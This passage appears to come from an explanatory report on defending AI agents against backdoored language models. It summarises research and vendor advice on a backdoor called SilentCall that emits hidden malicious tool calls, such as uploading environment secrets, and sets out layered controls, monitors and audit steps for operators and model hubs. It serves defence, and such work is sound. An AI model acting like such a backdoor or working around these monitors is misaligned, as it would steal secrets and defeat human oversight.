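In November 2026, Microsoft published advice with its research on Lazarus. Zeng and colleagues advise companies and individual users to find out where a model came from, limit its permissions, and log its commands, file changes and network traffic. They also recommend requiring approval before generated commands run, files change or data leaves the system. They add that a model's popularity is not evidence that it is safe.

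Microsoft's security team gives similar advice, according to Help Net Security. It recommends running generated code in isolated sandboxes, restricting outbound traffic, and comparing each checkpoint with its declared base model before deployment and after every update. The team recommends human approval only for high-impact calls, such as those that run commands or change permissions. Even this narrower rule covers most of a coding agent's work, because the agent works mainly by running commands. An operator would have to decide which commands count as high-impact, and a classifier like SilentCall's could help.

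For model hubs and vendors, Zeng and colleagues recommend auditing weights with capable AI agents, comparing models with their declared bases, and showing each model's origin and audit status before anyone downloads it. They also want companies to test agent platforms with backdoored models as well as injections. This advice is useful for operators too, and they can easily test most of the controls in this section by having a script emit the malicious calls directly, without a backdoored model.

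Microsoft says it is applying some of this to Foundry, its platform for hosting models. According to *Microsoft научилась прятать бэкдор в 10 нейронах* (2026), a Russian-language news report, the measures include checking where models come from, scanning their containers and accepting models only from trusted publishers. Automated weight analysis and cryptographic signatures are still in development.

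Kevin Kirkwood of Exabeam told ITPro that the advice to use AI auditors came without detection rates, false-positive rates or costs at scale. The research paper reports both rates, but only for edits that its own researchers made. The advice on permissions and outbound traffic doesn't depend on those rates because it doesn't require anyone to recognise the backdoor.

### An order of deployment

A small team should start with controls that work without recognising an attack, and add the ones that need tuning later. A reasonable order is:

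1. Remove tools, files and credentials that the agent doesn't need. SilentCall's upload is worth little to the attacker if the environment variables contain no secrets.
2. Run the agent in a sandbox and allow outbound traffic only to the hosts it uses.
3. Log every executed call with its full arguments, along with the context the model read. The replay test needs both.
4. Write code that checks recipients, sites and file paths against the request or a fixed list.
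5. Require approval, with the raw arguments, for the few actions that nobody can undo.
6. Add a classifier and a judge from a different model family. Let them record their decisions for a week or two before they block anything, so that the team learns the false-alarm rate on its own traffic.

The first two steps take some setup but need little attention afterwards. A team whose agent only reads documents and drafts text may not need the last step.

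A model hub has a different job, because it distributes models and doesn't usually see the calls they make. It could proceed as follows:

1. Record each model's publisher, declared base and file hash, and display them before download.
2. Scan every upload for added operations and unusual weights, and compare it with its declared base. Repeat this for updates and compressed versions.
3. Send the flagged models to an AI auditor, and have a person review the result before withdrawing anything.
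4. Run the most downloaded models as agents in a sandbox, varying the date, tools and input length, and check the calls they emit.
5. Publish the audit status with a warning that a model can pass and still be unsafe.

The fourth step takes the most resources, so it comes after the automated scans. It is also the only step that examines tool calls, so it could reveal a backdoor like SilentCall's that leaves the file format and the operations unchanged. A hub that runs models for its customers could also screen each tool call as the model emits it, but the customer's harness would still need to hold the call until the check finished.
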